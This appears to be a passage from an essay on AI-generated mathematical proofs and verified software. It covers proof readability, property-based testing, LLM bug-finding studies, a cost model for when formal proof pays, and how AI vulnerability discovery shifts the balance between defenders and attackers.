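Mathematicians want to know why a theorem is true as well as whether it is. Most of them already believed the Riemann hypothesis, and Tao said in March that people prize such problems partly because a solution should require new mathematics. James Maynard of the University of Oxford was "super excited" by Alpöge's proof but found its origin in AI slightly unsatisfying. Alpöge himself says he published the argument before mastering much of the mathematics around it, according to Mint's *Two separate maths groups confirm Anthropic’s Levent Alpöge solved the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026).

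An unreadable proof can still help people reach an explanation. Sernau's team could remove more than 99% of the code and have a checker confirm that nothing essential was missing. As Techno-Science's *Riemann hypothesis* (2026) points out, this lets an AI explore first and simplify later. Shortening an ordinary argument that much would be risky, because each cut could introduce an unnoticed mistake. People who write explanations can also consult the formal proof when a step is unclear.

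Proof also lets outsiders check a result without trusting the company that produced it. OpenAI has not released the model behind its manuscripts, so nobody else can measure how reliable it is. Few organisations could afford to repeat the work on Navier-Stokes, but anyone can run the Lean proof, as The Next Web's *OpenAI publishes its Navier-Stokes proof* observes. This advantage does not shrink as models improve, because even if a company had a model that was never wrong, other people would still need a reason to believe it.

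Some mathematicians try to provide both kinds of proof from the start. When Claude found a new result about the same function in August, two of Anthropic's mathematicians examined the argument while another employee worked with Claude on a Lean version. Axiom has published journal papers that pair a readable proof with a formal one, according to Axios' *AI math startup's proofs land in peer-reviewed journals* (2026).

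Readability matters less for software. Hardly anybody reads the machine code a compiler produces, and the users of a verified program need to understand what its proof proves, but not why the proof works.

### Testing properties instead of proving them

In software, the main alternative to proof is better testing. In property-based testing, a programmer states a property that should always hold, and a tool generates many inputs to look for a case where the property fails. Hatfield-Dodds maintains Hypothesis, a property-based testing tool for Python with roughly a million users. The following test is for a function that splits a bill, in pence, between several people.

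```
@given(integers(0, 100_000), integers(1, 50))
def test_split(total, people):
    assert sum(split(total, people)) == total
```

Suppose the function divides the total by the number of people and rounds down. Three people who share a bill of 100 pence pay 33 each, leaving a penny unpaid. Hypothesis soon finds such a failure, then looks for the simplest one, which here is a bill of one penny for two people.

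The programmer needs to write only one line about what the function should do, without loop invariants or a complete specification. Hatfield-Dodds describes this as going directly from properties to the implementation. Like any test, a property-based test can miss rare faults, although Hypothesis makes this less likely by favouring awkward values such as zero.

LLMs can now write such tests. In 2025, Maaz, DeVoe, Hatfield-Dodds and Carlini had an agent read the code and documentation of 100 popular Python packages, work out properties, and test them. In a sample the researchers reviewed by hand, 56% of the agent's bug reports were valid, and 32% were both valid and worth sending to the package's maintainers. Finding a valid bug cost about $10 in model use. One was in NumPy, a numerical library, where a function that should return only positive random numbers sometimes returned negative ones.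 Many of the false alarms came from the specification problem, because the agent had expected something the developers never promised.

LLMs can also look for bugs by reading code. Semgrep, a company that sells code analysis, tried this on 11 open-source web applications in 2025. Claude Code found 46 real vulnerabilities, but 86% of its reports were false alarms. OpenAI's Codex found 21, with 82% false alarms. Newer models do better. In early 2026, Claude Opus 4.6 found 22 vulnerabilities in Firefox in two weeks, and Mozilla, which makes the browser, rated 14 of them high-severity.

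Reviewing false alarms can cost more than running the model. If an engineer earns $100 an hour and needs half an hour to assess a report, each report costs $50. Based on the share of reports that were correct, that comes to about $360 per real vulnerability for Claude Code in the Semgrep test and about $90 per valid bug for the property-testing agent. A failed property test includes an input that reproduces the problem, so the engineer may need less than half an hour to assess it.

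There is little direct evidence of how testing compares with proof on the same code. The seL4 proof revealed many defects that had not surfaced in earlier use, but nobody had tried to test the kernel as thoroughly as possible. The fuzzing of lean-zip began only after the proofs were finished. Nobody seems to have published a fair comparison, which would give an LLM the same budget for testing and for proof on the same programs.

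Programmers can use both testing and proof. The property in the bill-splitting test could also serve as a postcondition in a verifier. Testing it first makes sense, because a counterexample that takes a second to find can save hours of trying to prove a false property.

### When does proof pay?

Suppose testing leaves a chance p that a program contains a serious fault, and a proof would remove a share r of such faults. If k products use the program and each would lose an amount L, the proof pays if

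p · r · k · L > C,

where C is the cost of writing the proof and keeping it up to date.

For an encryption library with p = 2%, r = 50%, k = 1,000 and L = $100,000, the proof is worth $1 million, five times its $200,000 cost. If the other values stayed the same, the proof would be worth $1,000 for an internal tool that only one company uses (k = 1).

Suppose better models write code with a tenth as many faults. The proof of the library is then worth only $100,000, and the objection is right that it no longer pays at the old price. But if the same models also cut the cost of the proof to $20,000, it is again worth five times what it costs. Whether proof remains worthwhile therefore depends on how fast its cost falls relative to the number of faults. The cost of proofs has clearly fallen fast, as the 17 hours for Navier-Stokes and the improved vericoding scores suggest. There is no comparable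 record for serious faults in software that people use.

The formula assumes that faults are triggered by accident, which is too optimistic when someone is looking for them. In a service that handles a million inputs a day, a fault that affects one input in a billion will occur by chance about once every three years, but an attacker who knows the input can trigger it every day. If a new model makes such faults ten times rarer, ordinary users will encounter a tenth as many, but one remaining fault may be enough for an attacker.

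A stable specification keeps C low, because each change to it may require a new proof. AI agents can also lower C, as Ochem's repaired proof suggests, but they can't help as much if the developers keep changing what the program should do.

| Software | Cost of a failure | Attackers | Specification | Reuse | Best approach |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Encryption library | High | Many | Exact and stable | Very wide | Proof and tests |
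| Compiler for aircraft software | High | Few | Long but stable | Wide | Proof and tests |
| Online shop | Moderate | Many | Changes often | One company | Tests, with proof for payment rules |
| Program that sorts holiday photos | Low | Few | Mostly a matter of taste | Varies | Tests |

The online shop is the hardest case, because it has determined attackers but no stable specification. Its owner can still benefit from proof indirectly by using verified libraries for encryption and reading files. The makers of those libraries can spread the cost of proof over thousands of customers.

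### When attackers have the same tools

AI that finds vulnerabilities cheaply helps both the people who maintain software and those who attack it. After Claude Opus 4.6 found the faults in Firefox, Anthropic spent about $4,000 having it try to turn them into working attacks. It succeeded only twice, in a test environment without some of the browser's protections. Anthropic repeated the test with its next major model, Claude Mythos Preview, which succeeded 181 times.

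Whether defenders or attackers gain more from AI depends partly on whether they find the same faults. Suppose a program has 100 faults. Without AI, the defenders find and fix half, and the attackers find 2% of the rest, which is one fault. With AI, the defenders find and fix 90%, and the attackers find half of the rest, which is five. The attackers have more faults to exploit than before, even though the program has far fewer left. To reduce the attackers' share to one fault again, the defenders would have to find and fix 98%.

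This assumes that attackers are as likely to find the faults that defenders missed as the ones that defenders found. If both sides use similar models, the faults that remain will tend to be ones that neither side can find. Defenders who search first then have a large advantage, if users install the repairs. But if a longer search keeps finding new faults, the advantage goes to whoever can spend more. Willison notes that Anthropic spent $100,000 on tokens in a search for cryptographic weaknesses. A bank or a criminal group could afford this, but most volunteers who maintain free software could not.

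A sound proof that a program never writes outside its memory rules out every fault of that kind, however much an attacker spends looking for one. Clark Barrett's company &Truth and its competitors hope to sell this kind of protection. But proving that a program carries out an encryption method correctly doesn't help if the method is weak. Metz points out that designers cannot anticipate everything that will go wrong once people use an application, so a company with verified software must keep testing it.
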